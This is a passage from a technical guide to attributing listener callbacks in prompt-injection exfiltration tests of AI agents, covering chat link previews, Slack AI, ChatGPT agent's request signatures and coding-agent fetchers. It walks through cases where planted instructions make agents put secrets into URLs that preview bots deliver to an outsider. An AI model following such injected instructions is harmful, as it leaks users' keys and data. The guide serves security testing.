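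One image link can bring all three. Embrace The Red's *Security Advisory* reports separate requests from each of them after an agent posted such a link, so the listener's log might look like this (invented, with the order chosen for illustration):

```
10:42:07   GET /i.png?d=blue-heron   User-Agent: Slackbot-LinkExpanding 1.0 ...
10:42:08   GET /i.png?d=blue-heron   User-Agent: Slackbot 1.0 ...
10:42:08   GET /i.png?d=blue-heron   User-Agent: Slack-ImgProxy ...
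```

These are three callbacks from one message. A tester who counted them as three leaks would overstate the result.

Cloudflare's *Telegram Bot* gives Telegram's user agent as `TelegramBot (like TwitterBot)`, and a server log from November 2025 on Wikimedia Phabricator contains the same text. A search for "TwitterBot" would match these requests and could lead a tester to attribute them to Twitter. Centinel Analytica's *TelegramBot* says that Telegram publishes the addresses its bot uses and that Centinel checks requests against them.

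The Apple Messages user agent is more misleading. In Bellingcat's test, it began like Safari on a Mac and ended with the names of Facebook's and Twitter's bots. Apple probably included those names so that websites would send Messages the same preview information they send Facebook and Twitter. The request came from the tester's own address, whereas a genuine Facebook preview came from an address registered to Facebook. Another clue that the request came from Messages was that it also fetched a file called `apple-touch-icon-precomposed.png`. Counting preview bots by user agent alone could attribute these requests to the wrong company.

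Discord gives the clearest instructions. It advises website owners to look for "Discordbot" in the user agent, since the rest of the string may change, and then to check the IP address against its official list. Discord also proxies images and may keep copies for later viewers.

Teams is harder to identify. Bellingcat found that Skype, another Microsoft product, sent preview requests from a Microsoft address with `SkypeUriPreview` in the user agent. It is reasonable to look for that string in a Teams test, but a tester should first post a harmless link in Teams and check what request arrives.

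People investigating a link can also trigger a preview bot's request. A Bellingcat author once sent phishing emails as part of an authorised security test and then noticed connections from Skype's servers. The client's incident response team was discussing the phishing site in a Skype chat, and Skype was previewing it. Testers can cause the same confusion by pasting a planted URL into their team's chat. Replacing the dots in the address with `[.]` prevents the chat application from recognising it as a link.

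### Slack AI: a leak that needed a click

An AI product inside a chat application can leak data without a preview bot. In August 2024, PromptArmor's *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via Indirect Prompt Injection* described a leak from Slack AI, a feature that answers questions about a workspace's messages.

In PromptArmor's example, a user stores an API key in a private channel. An attacker with access to the workspace, but not to that channel, posts a prompt injection in a public channel. When the user asks Slack AI for the key, Slack AI retrieves both messages. Its answer looks like an error message with a link to sign in again, and the link's URL contains the key. The key reaches the attacker's server only if the user clicks the link.

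The user's browser is therefore the fetcher. The listener receives the user's network address and the headers the browser sends on a click, as with a link in OpenAI's log viewer. The callback may arrive minutes or days after the answer, or never. In the OpenClaw case, the preview request should arrive soon after the message and doesn't reveal the user's address.

| | OpenClaw on Telegram | Slack AI |
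|---|---|---|
| Trigger | The agent's message is posted | The user clicks |
| Fetcher | Telegram's preview bot | The user's browser |
| Private data reaches the listener | Yes | Yes |
| User's network address reaches the listener | No | Yes |

A request from Slackbot during a Slack AI test would need another explanation. For example, the user might have copied the answer into a channel, where Slack previewed the link like any other.

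Neither the callback nor Slack AI's answer necessarily shows who planted the injection. In PromptArmor's main example, Slack AI cited only the private channel that held the key, although it had also used the outsider's message. In a second example, which led the user to a phishing page, Slack AI cited the planted message.

PromptArmor reported the problem on 14 August 2024. Slack replied five days later that the evidence was insufficient. It said the information in PromptArmor's first video came from a public channel, and that letting all members search public channels was "intended behavior". The reply did not address the leak of a key from a private channel. Willison (2024), in *Data Exfiltration from Slack AI via indirect prompt injection*, took the reply as a sign that Slack did not yet understand the problem.

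### Switching previews off as a fix and a test

An agent's developer can turn off Slack's link previews in the agent's messages with two settings, `unfurl_links` for text pages and `unfurl_media` for images, video and audio. Slack says both must be `false` to prevent it from crawling a link. If only `unfurl_links` is off, an image URL can still cause a callback.

The same settings can show whether a preview caused a callback:

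1. Post a new URL with previews on, and confirm that the listener receives a request.
2. Turn previews off, change nothing else, and post another new URL.
3. Turn previews back on and post a third.

If only the first and third URLs produce callbacks, the preview almost certainly caused them. If the second also produces one, something else can fetch the URL, such as the agent's browsing tool, a security scanner or a person who clicked. Using a new URL each time avoids Slack's cache.

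A model may write the link in one run and leave it out in the next, so the tester must check that all three links appeared in the chat. A short script that posts fixed messages avoids this problem. Embrace The Red used one to post a link to Slack, and the server recorded a request from Slackbot-LinkExpanding. The script tests only the platform's behavior, so the tester needs a separate test to show that the agent would write such a link.

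According to Slack's documentation, Slack previews all links by default, but in one of the documentation's examples, a link to a text page gets no preview unless the message sets `unfurl_links` to `true`. It is therefore safest to set both unfurl options explicitly in every step. Slack also doesn't preview a link whose visible label is just part of its URL without the `https://`, so such a label could make a vulnerable agent look safe.

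Embrace The Red used these settings to confirm a flaw in an MCP server that Anthropic had published for connecting AI agents to Slack. An MCP server is a program that offers tools to a model through a common standard called the Model Context Protocol. In one demonstration, a developer asks Claude Code, Anthropic's coding agent, to analyse a file with invisible instructions. The agent reads secrets from the developer's settings file and posts a link containing them to Slack. Slack's preview request then sends the secrets to the outsider.

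The developer might have let the agent post without approval because it could write to only one private channel. That restriction limits who can read the message but not where Slack sends its preview request. After Embrace The Red set both preview options to `false`, Slack stopped making previews.

On Telegram, OpenClaw users can add `linkPreview: false` to the Telegram section of the configuration file, which PromptArmor says stops data from reaching its test site. On Slack, the link preview setting, `unfurlLinks`, is off by default, according to OpenClaw's documentation, so a tester might get no callback and wrongly conclude that the model ignored the injection. The documentation gives no default for `unfurlMedia`, so image links need a separate test.

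These settings do not remove the link. A user can still click it, and the callback then comes from the user's browser. A user can also copy the link into a new message, where the agent's settings would not apply.

### The agent's developer and the chat platform

Responsibility for the leak is divided because neither company controls the whole process. The agent's developer decides what data the model can read and how the agent posts messages, and the chat platform makes the request that delivers the data. To the platform, a URL containing a stolen key can look like any other long URL. The developer may not realise that posting to a private chat can trigger a request to an outside server.

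PromptArmor wants chat platforms to offer preview settings, and agent developers to use them or pass the choice on to users. PromptArmor's own wording is more balanced than Apostol's article, which says that PromptArmor places most of the responsibility on the platforms. PromptArmor also suggests settings for individual chats or channels, which would let an administrator protect a channel without relying on the developer of every agent that posts there.

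Slack generally previews links from both apps and people by default, but it advises developers to consider disabling previews for messages from a language model. Slack also ignores `robots.txt`, partly because, it says, its bots act "on behalf of a human". That reasoning is less convincing when an agent posts a link that no person has seen.

Anthropic did not patch its Slack server. Embrace The Red reported the flaw on 27 May 2025, and Anthropic archived the software two days later, though it is unclear whether the report was the reason. Anthropic had no plans to fix vulnerabilities in its archived servers and agreed to public disclosure. The package still had more than 14,000 downloads a week at the time. Embrace The Red argues that any AI software that posts to a chat application should disable previews by default, perhaps with an option to allow them for chosen websites.

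Discord's page explains how its previews work but does not discuss links written by AI agents. If a platform has no suitable setting, the developer can either remove links from the agent's messages or allow only links to trusted sites. Either would also reduce the risk from users clicking links, which preview settings don't affect.

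## A signed request and two misleading crawlers: ChatGPT agent

Slack's and Telegram's preview bots name themselves in the user agent. ChatGPT agent, a feature that operated a web browser for the user, sent an ordinary browser's user agent and identified itself with a cryptographic signature. In *ChatGPT agent’s user-agent*, Willison (2025) published the full headers of a request he captured on 4 August 2025. He also explains how he came to believe, wrongly, that ChatGPT had leaked his test URLs to two search engines.

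Willison made a page on his website that logged every request, then asked the agent to open and describe it. The agent reported a heading, some text and a line that a script had added. The fetcher had therefore run the page's JavaScript, as a browser does, unlike a simple download program.

### The captured headers

The request passed through Cloudflare, the CDN in front of Willison's site, and then through Heroku, the company that hosts it. Both added headers. These are the most useful ones, shortened and grouped by the software that wrote them:

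```
Agent's browser
  User-Agent           Mozilla/5.0 (Macintosh; ...) ... Chrome/138.0.0.0 ...
  Sec-Ch-Ua            "Not)A;Brand";v="8", "Chromium";v="138"
  Sec-Ch-Ua-Platform   "Linux"
  Sec-Fetch-Site       none
  Sec-Fetch-User       ?1

OpenAI's signing software
  Signature-Agent      "https://chatgpt.com"
  Signature-Input      sig1=(...);created=1754340838;...
  Signature            sig1=:1Axf...:

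Cloudflare
  Cf-Connecting-Ip     2a09:bac5:665f:1541::21e:154
  Cf-Ray               96a0f289adcb8e8e-SEA

Heroku
  Via                  1.1 heroku-router
  X-Request-Start      1754340840059
```

Willison also printed requests from two search crawlers, which help separate the hosting's headers from the agent's. Headers such as Cf-Ray and Via appear in all three requests, so they come from the hosting. Accept-Encoding has the same value in all three (`gzip, br`), which suggests Cloudflare rewrote it. Treating that value as a trait of the fetcher would be a mistake.

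The User-Agent header describes Chrome on a Mac, so anyone who read only that header would have attributed the request to a person's browser. The Sec-Fetch headers, which match those a browser sends when someone types an address, would have reinforced the mistake. Willison briefly wondered whether ChatGPT agent had copied his own browser's user agent, but he was using Firefox.

The client hints don't match that description. They list the platform as Linux, and the brands include Chromium, the open-source browser on which Chrome is based, but not Google Chrome. Something had evidently changed the user agent. That alone doesn't point to an AI agent, since a person on Linux can also set a browser's user agent to Chrome on a Mac. Known Agents' *What Is ChatGPT Agent?* gives an example from after Willison's test that still describes a Mac, with Chrome 144.

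The request also contained a `cf_clearance` cookie, which Cloudflare gives to browsers that pass its bot checks. The agent's browser had probably encountered Cloudflare before this request, perhaps on a check page that Cloudflare served without contacting the listener. Scrunch (2025) found that such checks interrupted some requests from Operator, the agent's predecessor.

### Who owned the source address

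Cloudflare recorded the agent's source address in Cf-Connecting-Ip. The X-Forwarded-For header lists the same address, followed by 172.71.147.183, the address of the Cloudflare machine that connected to Heroku. Because the request passed through two intermediaries before reaching the listener, the last entry is not the agent's address.

The registry record on bash.ws, a network lookup site, shows that the agent's address belongs to a Cloudflare block named CLOUDFLAREWARP. WARP is a Cloudflare service that works much like a VPN. Cf-Connecting-Ip contained a Microsoft address when Bingbot visited and a Yandex address when Yandex's crawler did, so the agent's address is not that of Willison's own CDN, though a tester could easily mistake it for that. The agent's browser apparently reached the internet through Cloudflare's network. The record doesn't show where the browser ran or who arranged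 the route.

People use WARP too. Together, the address and the user agent would have described someone with a Mac and a VPN.

Checking OpenAI's address files would not have corrected this. DataDome's *Detecting & Authenticating ChatGPT Agent* says the agent, unlike ChatGPT-User, had neither identifiable addresses nor a reverse DNS name that a website could verify. In January 2025, Scrunch had found the same problem with Operator, whose requests came from Microsoft's cloud and from addresses OpenAI had not published.

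### What OpenAI signed

According to DataDome, OpenAI began adding digital signatures to the agent's requests on 25 July 2025, ten days before Willison's test. Producing a valid signature requires a private key, which the signer keeps secret. The signer publishes a matching public key that anyone can use to check the signature.

The IETF standard *HTTP Message Signatures* (Backman, Richer and Sporny, RFC 9421, February 2024) explains how to sign parts of a web request. Web Bot Auth adds rules for bots that use the standard, including where they publish their keys.

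A sender doesn't sign the whole request, because proxies may legitimately change some of it on the way. Instead, the sender chooses certain parts and combines them into a short text called the signature base. For Willison's request it would look like this:

```
"@authority": simonwillison.net
"@method": GET
"@path": /test-url-context
"signature-agent": "https://chatgpt.com"
"@signature-params": ("@authority" "@method" "@path" "signature-agent")
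    ;created=1754340838;keyid="otMq..."
    ;expires=1754344438;nonce="_8jb..."
    ;tag="web-bot-auth";alg="ed25519"
```

The captured headers don't include the method or the path, so those two lines are inferred from Willison's prompt. The final entry is a single line in the real text. It comes from the Signature-Input header, which lists the signed parts and describes the signature. The Signature header contains the result of the calculation:

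```
signature = Sign(private key, signature base)
Verify(public key, signature base, signature) = true or false
```

OpenAI's signature covered the request's method, path and `@authority` (the host name). *HTTP Message Signatures for Bots* (2025), an IETF draft from shortly before the test, required only that bots sign the `@authority`. Anyone who obtained a copy of a signature covering only the host name could use it for any page on that host until it expired.

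The signature did not cover the query string, which `@path` leaves out. In a request for `/i.png?d=blue-heron`, someone could change the marker "blue-heron" to another word and the same kind of signature would still be valid. Testers can avoid this gap by putting the marker in the path, which the signature does cover, as in `/k7q2/blue-heron.png`.

### Checking the signature

To verify a request like Willison's, a tester can follow these steps:

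1. Read Signature-Input to find the signed parts, the key's identifier and the times. Confirm that the tag is `web-bot-auth`.
2. Confirm that Signature-Agent is `https://chatgpt.com`, and download OpenAI's public keys from `/.well-known/http-message-signatures-directory` on that site.
3. Select the key that matches `keyid`.
4. Rebuild the signature base from the request that arrived.
5. Run the verification function for Ed25519, the signature method named in this request.
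6. Compare the creation and expiry times with the time of arrival.

Step 2 is essential because anyone can publish keys on their own domain and produce valid signatures with them. Anyone can also write OpenAI's address in the Signature-Agent header, but the check in step 5 will fail unless they signed the request with OpenAI's private key.

Backman and colleagues recommend testing the checking program on invalid signatures as well as valid ones, since a program that accepts everything would pass a test that used only genuine requests. Changing one letter of the path should make verification fail.

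Willison explains in his post how to check the signature but doesn't say that he did. The attribution is still convincing because the request arrived when he gave the agent a new URL, and the agent then described the page.

Castle, a bot-detection company, published a worked example with the same key that Willison's request used. The key's expiry date was 8 August 2025, four days after his test. OpenAI may remove old keys from its site, so testers should save a copy of the key file with the log, as they would with an address file. When checking an old log, they should compare the signature's expiry with the request's arrival time, not with today's date.

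The listener's hosting can also make a genuine signature fail verification. Heroku's headers show that Cloudflare connected to Heroku over HTTP, although the agent had used HTTPS. This didn't affect verification because OpenAI had not signed the full URL. If OpenAI had signed it, a program that rebuilt the URL from Heroku's connection would have started it with `http://` and rejected the signature.

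Sometimes a tester can't complete the check, for example because the key file is unavailable. *HTTP Message Signatures for automated traffic* (Meunier and Major, 2026), the current draft of Web Bot Auth, treats such a request as "unverified" rather than "invalid". Failing to download the key file is not evidence that the request is fake.

### Creation time, expiry and nonce

A valid signature still verifies no matter how many times anyone sends it. Without further limits, someone who copied the headers could replay the request months later and make it look like a new visit from ChatGPT.

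The creation and expiry times, given in Unix time (seconds since the start of 1970), limit how long a copy is useful. OpenAI's software created the signature at 20:53:58 UTC, and Heroku received the request about two seconds later. The signature expired exactly one hour after its creation, within the 24-hour maximum that the current draft recommends.

The nonce, a random value made for one signature, can expose a replay within that hour. If two requests contain the same nonce, at least one is probably a copy. To detect this, the listener has to record the nonces it receives and check each new request against them.

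HTTPS prevents outsiders from copying the signature in transit, but the listener's CDN and hosting company can read it, as can anyone who receives the log. It is best to publish a signature only after it has expired.

### What a valid signature leaves open

If Willison's request passes the check, someone holding the private key for one of OpenAI's published public keys signed a request for that page at about that time. Unless OpenAI had lost control of the private key, the request came from OpenAI's software. A valid signature is much better evidence of this than the user agent, and it holds even though the address belongs to Cloudflare.

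The signature on a ChatGPT agent request doesn't identify the user, the conversation or the prompt. Cloudflare classes the agent's access as "intermediary", meaning that end users can control what the bot does. All their requests could be signed with the same key. A tester can connect a request to a particular run by using a new path each time, because the signature covers the path.

The signature also doesn't prove that a model chose to open the URL. *Proof-of-Agentness* (2026) points out that an ordinary script can use an authenticated agent identity too. OpenAI's *ChatGPT agent* says that users could take over the agent's remote browser, for example to log in to a website. If OpenAI also signed those requests, a person's click could have produced a request with a valid signature.

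The signature also doesn't show whether the visit was harmful. An agent can produce an equally valid signature whether it opens a page because its user asked or because of a prompt injection. To tell these cases apart, the tester needs the conversation and the data in the URL.

A missing signature is even weaker evidence. Most web requests are unsigned, and Meunier and Major say that a website learns nothing about the sender from a missing signature.

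### Who signs requests in 2026

ChatGPT agent is no longer available. OpenAI now directs users to ChatGPT Work, whose cloud browser signs its requests in the same way, according to its *ChatGPT Work's Cloud browser allowlisting*. The security companies Akamai and HUMAN still list this traffic as "ChatGPT Agent", so a tester may see the old name in their dashboards.

Google's *Authenticate requests with Web Bot Auth (experimental)* says that Google signs some of Google-Agent's requests, and Google's *Changelog* dates this documentation to 4 May 2026. Lumar's *Web Bot Auth directory* from August 2026 lists Amazon's hosted browser for AI agents as an adopter. Citing DataDome's findings, Rijo (2026) reports in *Meta's Muse agent gains a signed ID in a quiet test* that Meta joined the adopters in October.

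| Operator | Signed requests | Extent |
|---|---|---|
| OpenAI | ChatGPT Work's cloud browser | Each request |
| Google | Google-Agent | Some requests, as an experiment |
| Amazon | Bedrock AgentCore Browser | On by default |
| Meta | Muse and Meta-WebIndexer | Few requests, since about 12 October 2026 |

Akamai, Cloudflare, HUMAN and Vercel automatically verify OpenAI's signatures for websites that use their services, so many testers will not need to check them. If a listener is not behind such a service, the tester has to verify the signatures.

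HTTP Message Signatures is a published standard, but Web Bot Auth is not and is still changing. In August, Lumar noted that companies were using Web Bot Auth before the IETF's working group had adopted any document for it. The group's first draft, written by Cloudflare and Google employees, followed on 1 September 2026.

The draft now requires Signature-Agent to include a label, as in `sig1="https://chatgpt.com"`. OpenAI's instructions still show the address without a label, as does Willison's capture. The draft allows recipients to accept the old form but doesn't require them to, so a tester's strict checking program could reject a genuine request from OpenAI.

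### Bingbot and Yandex arrive

Just after the agent's visit, Willison's log recorded a second request for the same URL. He then tried a new URL, and a different crawler came:

```
20:54:00 UTC   ChatGPT agent   first test URL
20:55:16 UTC   Bingbot         first test URL
22:11:09 UTC   YandexBot       second test URL
```

Bingbot had arrived 76 seconds after the agent, at a URL that Willison had not published. He checked the crawler's IP address with Microsoft's lookup tool, which confirmed it was genuine. For Yandex, he ran a reverse DNS lookup and got a name ending in `spider.yandex.com`. He doesn't report the forward lookup that would complete this check, but what he learned later leaves little reason to doubt the result. Both crawlers also visited a third URL.

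Willison concluded that ChatGPT was somehow leaking the URLs. He ruled out his browser extensions because he had not opened the pages in his own browser. He also knew that the agent had made only one request to the page. He suspected a proxy on OpenAI's side, but he didn't understand how it could have learned the full URL, since HTTPS hides the path from machines that only relay traffic.

Cloudflare, the CDN for Willison's own site, has to decrypt each request to check whether it already has a copy of the page, so it had the full URL. Willison had listed Cloudflare as one of the steps between the agent and his server but had not considered it as the source of the leak.

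After he published his theory, a reader, Jatan Loya, asked whether he had Cloudflare's Crawler Hints switched on. He did, and had probably enabled it himself some time before. Cloudflare's *Crawler Hints* explains the feature, which produces this sequence:

1. ChatGPT agent requests a new URL.
2. Cloudflare has no stored copy of the page, so it fetches one from the website's server and records a cache miss.
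3. Crawler Hints treats the miss as a sign of new or changed content and reports the URL to IndexNow, a service that notifies search engines.
4. The search engines send their crawlers.

Microsoft Bing's *Cloudflare Supports IndexNow via one-click Integration* names Microsoft and Yandex as Cloudflare's partners in this arrangement, which explains why those two crawlers came.

Willison deleted his posts on Twitter and Bluesky and corrected the article. He also had to change the article's web address, because both platforms had stored a link preview with the incorrect title.

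### The control that was missing

The checks on Bingbot and Yandex established who had fetched the URLs, but not where the crawlers had got them. A genuine crawler would pass the same checks whether the URL came from OpenAI, Cloudflare or a public link.

Repeating the experiment didn't help either. ChatGPT's visits did lead to the crawlers' visits, so the pattern was bound to recur. But in all three tests, ChatGPT visited first and Cloudflare was in front of the site, so the tests could not separate their effects.

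Willison could have separated them by requesting a fresh URL without ChatGPT, for example with a command-line program on his own computer. The two explanations predict different results:

| Test with a new URL | If ChatGPT leaks it | If Crawler Hints reports it |
|---|---|---|
| ChatGPT agent opens it through Cloudflare | Crawlers come | Crawlers come |
| A command-line program opens it through Cloudflare | No crawlers | Crawlers come |
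| ChatGPT agent opens it on a server without a CDN | Crawlers come | No crawlers |

Willison ran the first test three times, but it can't distinguish between the explanations. Either of the other two tests would have. The second is quicker because it needs no new server.

One run of the control might not be enough. In Willison's account, each crawler visited two of the three URLs. If Bingbot visited two-thirds of the time, it would miss a single control run one time in three, but three in a row only about one time in 27. These figures are rough because they rest on so few tests. Watching for both crawlers also makes a false negative less likely.

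### Other requests caused by the listener's hosting

Crawler Hints applies to a whole website, so a tester who turned it on for an ordinary site may forget that it also affects any page planted there. The simplest remedy is to turn it off. A tester who needs it for the rest of the site can send the header `X-Robots-Tag: noindex` with planted pages, which Cloudflare says stops them from being indexed. The header has to be in place before the first visit, since that visit may be enough to alert the search engines.

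Other services can add requests. A hosting company may check that a server is running, and a monitoring service may load a page regularly. Scanners look for new host names in public HTTPS certificate logs and may visit a listener minutes after it gets a certificate.

The requested path helps to identify these visitors. A certificate log contains the host name but not `/k7q2/blue-heron.png`, so a scanner that found the listener through the log would usually request the home page or guess common file names. A visitor that requests the exact planted path must have learned it from something that handled the URL, which could be the AI product or the listener's CDN, hosting company or log-analysis service.

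These extra requests can also expose data. If Willison's URLs had contained a real password, his own CDN would have sent it to two search engines. This risk is a good reason to plant only harmless markers, even on a server the tester controls.

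## Coding agents: the developer's machine or the provider's cloud

ChatGPT agent worked in a remote browser, so its requests did not come from the user's network. Coding agents such as Claude Code and Codex read and change a developer's files, run commands and look things up on the web, usually while running on the developer's machine. Some make their web requests from that machine, while others have the provider's servers make them. Only requests made from the developer's machine reveal the developer's network address to a listener.

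### Seven tools and an echo page

Checkly's *The Current State of Content Negotiation for AI Agents (Feb 2026)* reports the headers that seven coding tools sent. Checkly, a website-monitoring company, wanted to know which tools ask for pages in Markdown, which uses fewer tokens than HTML. It had each tool open a page at httpbin.org that returns the request headers it receives.

| Tool | Version | User agent | Accept header |
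|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code | 2.1.38 | `axios/1.8.4` | `text/markdown, text/html, */*` |
| Cursor | 2.4.28 | `Mozilla/5.0 ... Chrome/139.0.0.0 Safari/537.36` | `text/markdown,text/html;q=0.9,...` |
| OpenCode | 1.2.5 | `Mozilla/5.0 ... Chrome/139.0.0.0 Safari/537.36` | `text/markdown;q=1.0,...` |
| Codex | 260203.1501 | `Mozilla/5.0 ... ChatGPT-User/1.0; ...` | `text/html,application/xhtml+xml,...` |
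| Gemini CLI | 0.28.2 | `GoogleAgent-URLContext` | `*/*` |
| GitHub Copilot | VS Code 1.109.3 | `Mozilla/5.0 ... Code/1.109.3 ... Electron/39.3.0` | `text/html,application/xhtml+xml,...` |
| Windsurf | 1.9552.21 | `colly - ...` | `*/*` |

Cursor and OpenCode sent the user agent of an ordinary browser, but their Accept headers distinguish them because they begin with `text/markdown` instead of a browser's `text/html`. A log search for `Google-Agent`, the name in Google's documentation, would miss Gemini CLI, which sent `GoogleAgent-URLContext`.

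The echo page returned headers but no source addresses, so the test shows the names the tools sent but not where their requests came from. The names `axios` and `colly` belong to programming libraries that can run on a laptop or in a data centre. Also, if a provider uses a stored copy of the echo page, the tool reports the headers of whatever fetched that copy, perhaps days earlier.

In *Developer Experience with AI Coding Agents*, Borysenko (2026) avoided the second problem by logging requests on his own server. He gave nine coding agents the same prompt three times each in February and March 2026, and each agent's headers stayed the same across its three runs. Claude Code and Windsurf used the same names as in Checkly's test, but Cursor's requests named `got`, a JavaScript library. Cursor also sent a HEAD request, which asks for a page's headers without its content, before the normal request.

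The two tests may have used different versions of Cursor. Cursor can also fetch pages in several ways, including through MCP servers, as rhyannonjoy found when comparing its web tools. A tester therefore needs to record both the product version and the tool the agent called.

Version numbers in these strings go out of date quickly, so searching for the names alone is best. Known Agents' *What is Code?*, for example, lists a later Copilot user agent with `Code/1.134.0` and `Electron/42.8.1`.

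### Where each tool's request starts

In *Inspecting Claude Code’s Network Traffic with Linux Namespaces and MITM Proxying*, McCanna investigated whether Claude Code fetches a page itself from the developer's machine or Anthropic's servers fetch it and pass it on. McCanna ran Claude Code in a Linux network namespace, which gives a program its own network interface and keeps other programs' traffic out of the capture.

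When Claude Code used WebFetch, its built-in tool for reading web pages, the capture showed a connection from the machine directly to the requested site. McCanna could see this without decrypting the traffic because the site's host name was sent unencrypted at the start of the connection. Decrypting the traffic then showed the request itself, which had a `Claude-User` user agent.

That name is new since Checkly's test. Anthropic now documents that WebFetch's user agent begins with `Claude-User`, the name its server-side fetcher also uses. Siteline, which measures AI agents' visits to websites, dates a distinct Claude Code user agent to late March 2026. It counts `claude-code` visits separately from other `claude-user` visits, so a site can use the full string to tell the two apart.

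Claude Code on the web runs in virtual machines that Anthropic manages, and their outgoing traffic passes through a security proxy, according to Anthropic's *Data usage*. A callback from one of those sessions would not come from the developer's address.

According to Google's *Web fetch tool (web_fetch)*, **Gemini CLI** first requests the page through Google's URL context service. If that fails, it tries to fetch the page directly from the developer's machine. The same prompt can therefore produce a callback from either Google's network or the developer's.

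The tester's choice of listener may determine whether the request comes from the developer's machine or the provider's cloud. According to Google's *URL context*, the service does not support tunnelling services such as ngrok, which testers often use to connect a listener on their own computer to the internet. Google's service should therefore refuse a tunnel URL, and Gemini CLI may then fetch it locally. A tester could wrongly conclude that Gemini CLI always fetches from the developer's machine, when it did so only because of the tunnel.

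**Codex.** The ChatGPT-User name in Checkly's test suggests that the fetch came from OpenAI's servers. For *What data do coding agents send, and where to?*, Pye intercepted the traffic of seven coding agents between July and September 2025. Apart from sites that its commands used, Codex contacted only `api.openai.com`. This is consistent with a fetch from OpenAI's servers, but it is weak evidence because none of Pye's tasks asked the agent to read a web page.

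Codex often fetches nothing. According to OpenAI's *Config basics*, Codex's web search uses an OpenAI index by default and requests pages only in "live" mode. Live mode becomes the default when the developer gives Codex full access to the machine. *Indexed Web Search* (Vaughan, 2026) describes a third mode, added on 22 June 2026, which allows live searches but opens only pages that OpenAI's servers approve.

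Borysenko traces Copilot's requests to VS Code's extension host, the part of the editor that runs add-ons, so the fetcher normally runs on the developer's machine. For Cursor and Windsurf, the published headers contain only the name of a browser or library, which is not enough to locate the fetcher. A tester can locate it by having the tool open a new URL and comparing the source address in the log with the machine's public address.

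| Tool | Where its built-in web tool fetches from | Evidence |
|---|---|---|
| Claude Code on a developer's machine | That machine | McCanna's traffic capture |
| Claude Code on the web | A virtual machine that Anthropic manages | Anthropic's documentation |
| Gemini CLI | Google's servers, with the developer's machine as a fallback | Google's documentation |
| Codex | OpenAI's servers, if it fetches the page at all | The ChatGPT-User name and OpenAI's documentation |
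| Copilot in VS Code | Most likely the developer's machine | Borysenko's analysis of its requests |
| Cursor and Windsurf | Not established | Header names only |

### A provider's name from an office address

Because Claude Code now uses Anthropic's name from developers' own networks, a listener may record something like this (an invented entry):

```
198.51.100.80   10:50:03 UTC   GET /k7q2/notes
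User-Agent: Claude-User (claude-code/...; ...)
Accept: text/markdown, text/html, */*
```

If a callback's user agent points to Anthropic but a registry lookup shows that the address belongs to a company's office, the request probably came from Claude Code running on a machine in that office. A tester would probably be wrong to conclude from the user agent that Anthropic's servers fetched the page, or to call the request a forgery because the address is not on Anthropic's published list.

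Anthropic's list could not include the address of every office and home where someone runs Claude Code. A service that verifies Claude-User by address alone would therefore count genuine Claude Code requests as fake. If the listener's CDN blocks these requests, the tester will get no callback.

| User agent | Source address | Most likely fetcher |
|---|---|---|
| `Claude-User` without `claude-code` | On Anthropic's list | Anthropic's servers |
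| `Claude-User` with `claude-code` | A home or office network | Claude Code on a machine there |
| `Claude-User` with `claude-code` | A data centre | Claude Code on the web or on a rented server, or a developer using a VPN |
| `ChatGPT-User` | In OpenAI's address files | OpenAI's servers, acting for ChatGPT or Codex |
| `ChatGPT-User` | A home or office network | A script or other program that copied the name |
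| `Code/` and `Electron/` | A home or office network | VS Code, possibly running Copilot |

The conclusion in the fifth row differs from the one in the second because the two products work differently. Anthropic documents a program that uses the Claude-User name on developers' machines. OpenAI's documentation doesn't describe Codex making ChatGPT-User requests from a developer's machine.

The last row also requires checking the Accept header, because VS Code can load an image that a model has written into a chat answer. The header for an image request should begin with image formats, whereas Copilot's page-fetching tool sent one that began with `text/html`.

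Forgery is unlikely in a controlled test if the tester gave a new URL to only one session and the callback came from the public address of the machine running that session. But the tester cannot tell from the listener's log alone which machine behind an office gateway made the request.

The number of requests can also help distinguish the two. In Borysenko's tests, the Claude chat service requested `robots.txt` and the page at the same time, from two addresses. Claude Code made a single request and did not fetch `robots.txt`. A listener whose `robots.txt` forbids everything might therefore stop the chat service but not the coding agent. These tests began before Claude Code changed its user agent, so they are worth repeating on a current version.

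### The built-in tool or a shell command

A coding agent can also fetch a URL by running a command such as `curl`. Anthropic warns that Claude Code can reach any URL this way, even if the developer has blocked WebFetch, when it is allowed to use its shell tool, Bash, outside the sandbox (a restricted environment for commands). Anthropic's *Tools reference* suggests `curl` when the agent needs the unprocessed page, because WebFetch usually returns a smaller model's answer about the page.

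The listener might then receive a second request from the same office (also invented):

```
198.51.100.80   10:50:41 UTC   GET /k7q2/notes
User-Agent: curl/8.4.0
Accept: */*
```

The address is the same because both fetchers run on the same machine. The user agent now identifies the program that the coding agent ran, and Claude's name doesn't appear anywhere in the request.

A name like this suggests that a shell command fetched the URL but does not prove it. Cline and Junie, two other coding agents in Borysenko's study, sent `curl/8.4.0` whenever he asked them to read a page. Claude Code's built-in tool sent the name of the library `axios` in February. A developer, rather than the agent, could also have typed the command.

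Codex can cause one callback from OpenAI's servers through its web tool and another from the developer's network through a command. When Pye asked agents to upload a test report to a file-sharing site, Codex did it with a command that connected from the test machine, although Codex itself communicated only with OpenAI. OpenAI turns off network access for commands by default in Codex's usual sandbox, and Pye had to approve a retry outside it.

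The agent's records are better evidence than the headers. Claude Code saves session transcripts as plain text under `~/.claude/projects/` and keeps them for 30 days by default. A tester can search them for the planted URL and see whether it appears in a WebFetch call or a Bash command. If the agent ran a script that contained the URL, the transcript may show only the script's name, so the tester would have to match the times of the command and the callback.

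Blocking WebFetch and repeating the test is less conclusive, because the second run does not show which route the agent used in the first. If a callback still arrives, the agent can reach the listener through a command, but it may have switched to that route only because WebFetch was unavailable.

A single prompt to an agent can also produce several callbacks so, as with Slack's preview bots, several callbacks do not mean that several leaks occurred. For one prompt, Borysenko's server received two requests from Cursor, three from Junie and four from Cline, because Junie read several pages and Cline also looked for API descriptions.

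### When a page produces no callback

An agent can read a page without contacting the server that hosts it. This commonly happens because the provider already has a copy in its index or the tool has a recent copy in its cache.

By default, Codex answers from OpenAI's index. Google's URL context service also checks an index first and requests the live page only if it finds no copy. OpenAI's *Offline web search for ChatGPT workspaces* describes a setting that limits ChatGPT's web search to indexed and cached pages, and some regulated workspaces have it on by default. If a planted page is already in one of these indexes, the model can read a prompt injection on it while the listener records nothing.

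An index-only tool cannot open a URL that the model has just created, so it cannot send private data to the listener in that URL. The absence of a callback does not show whether the model read the planted page, but it is better evidence that the tool did not send data in a new URL.

WebFetch keeps each response for 15 minutes by default. Suppose Claude Code reads the same URL three times:

| Time | What the agent does | What the listener records |
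|---|---|---|
| 10:00 | Reads the page | A callback |
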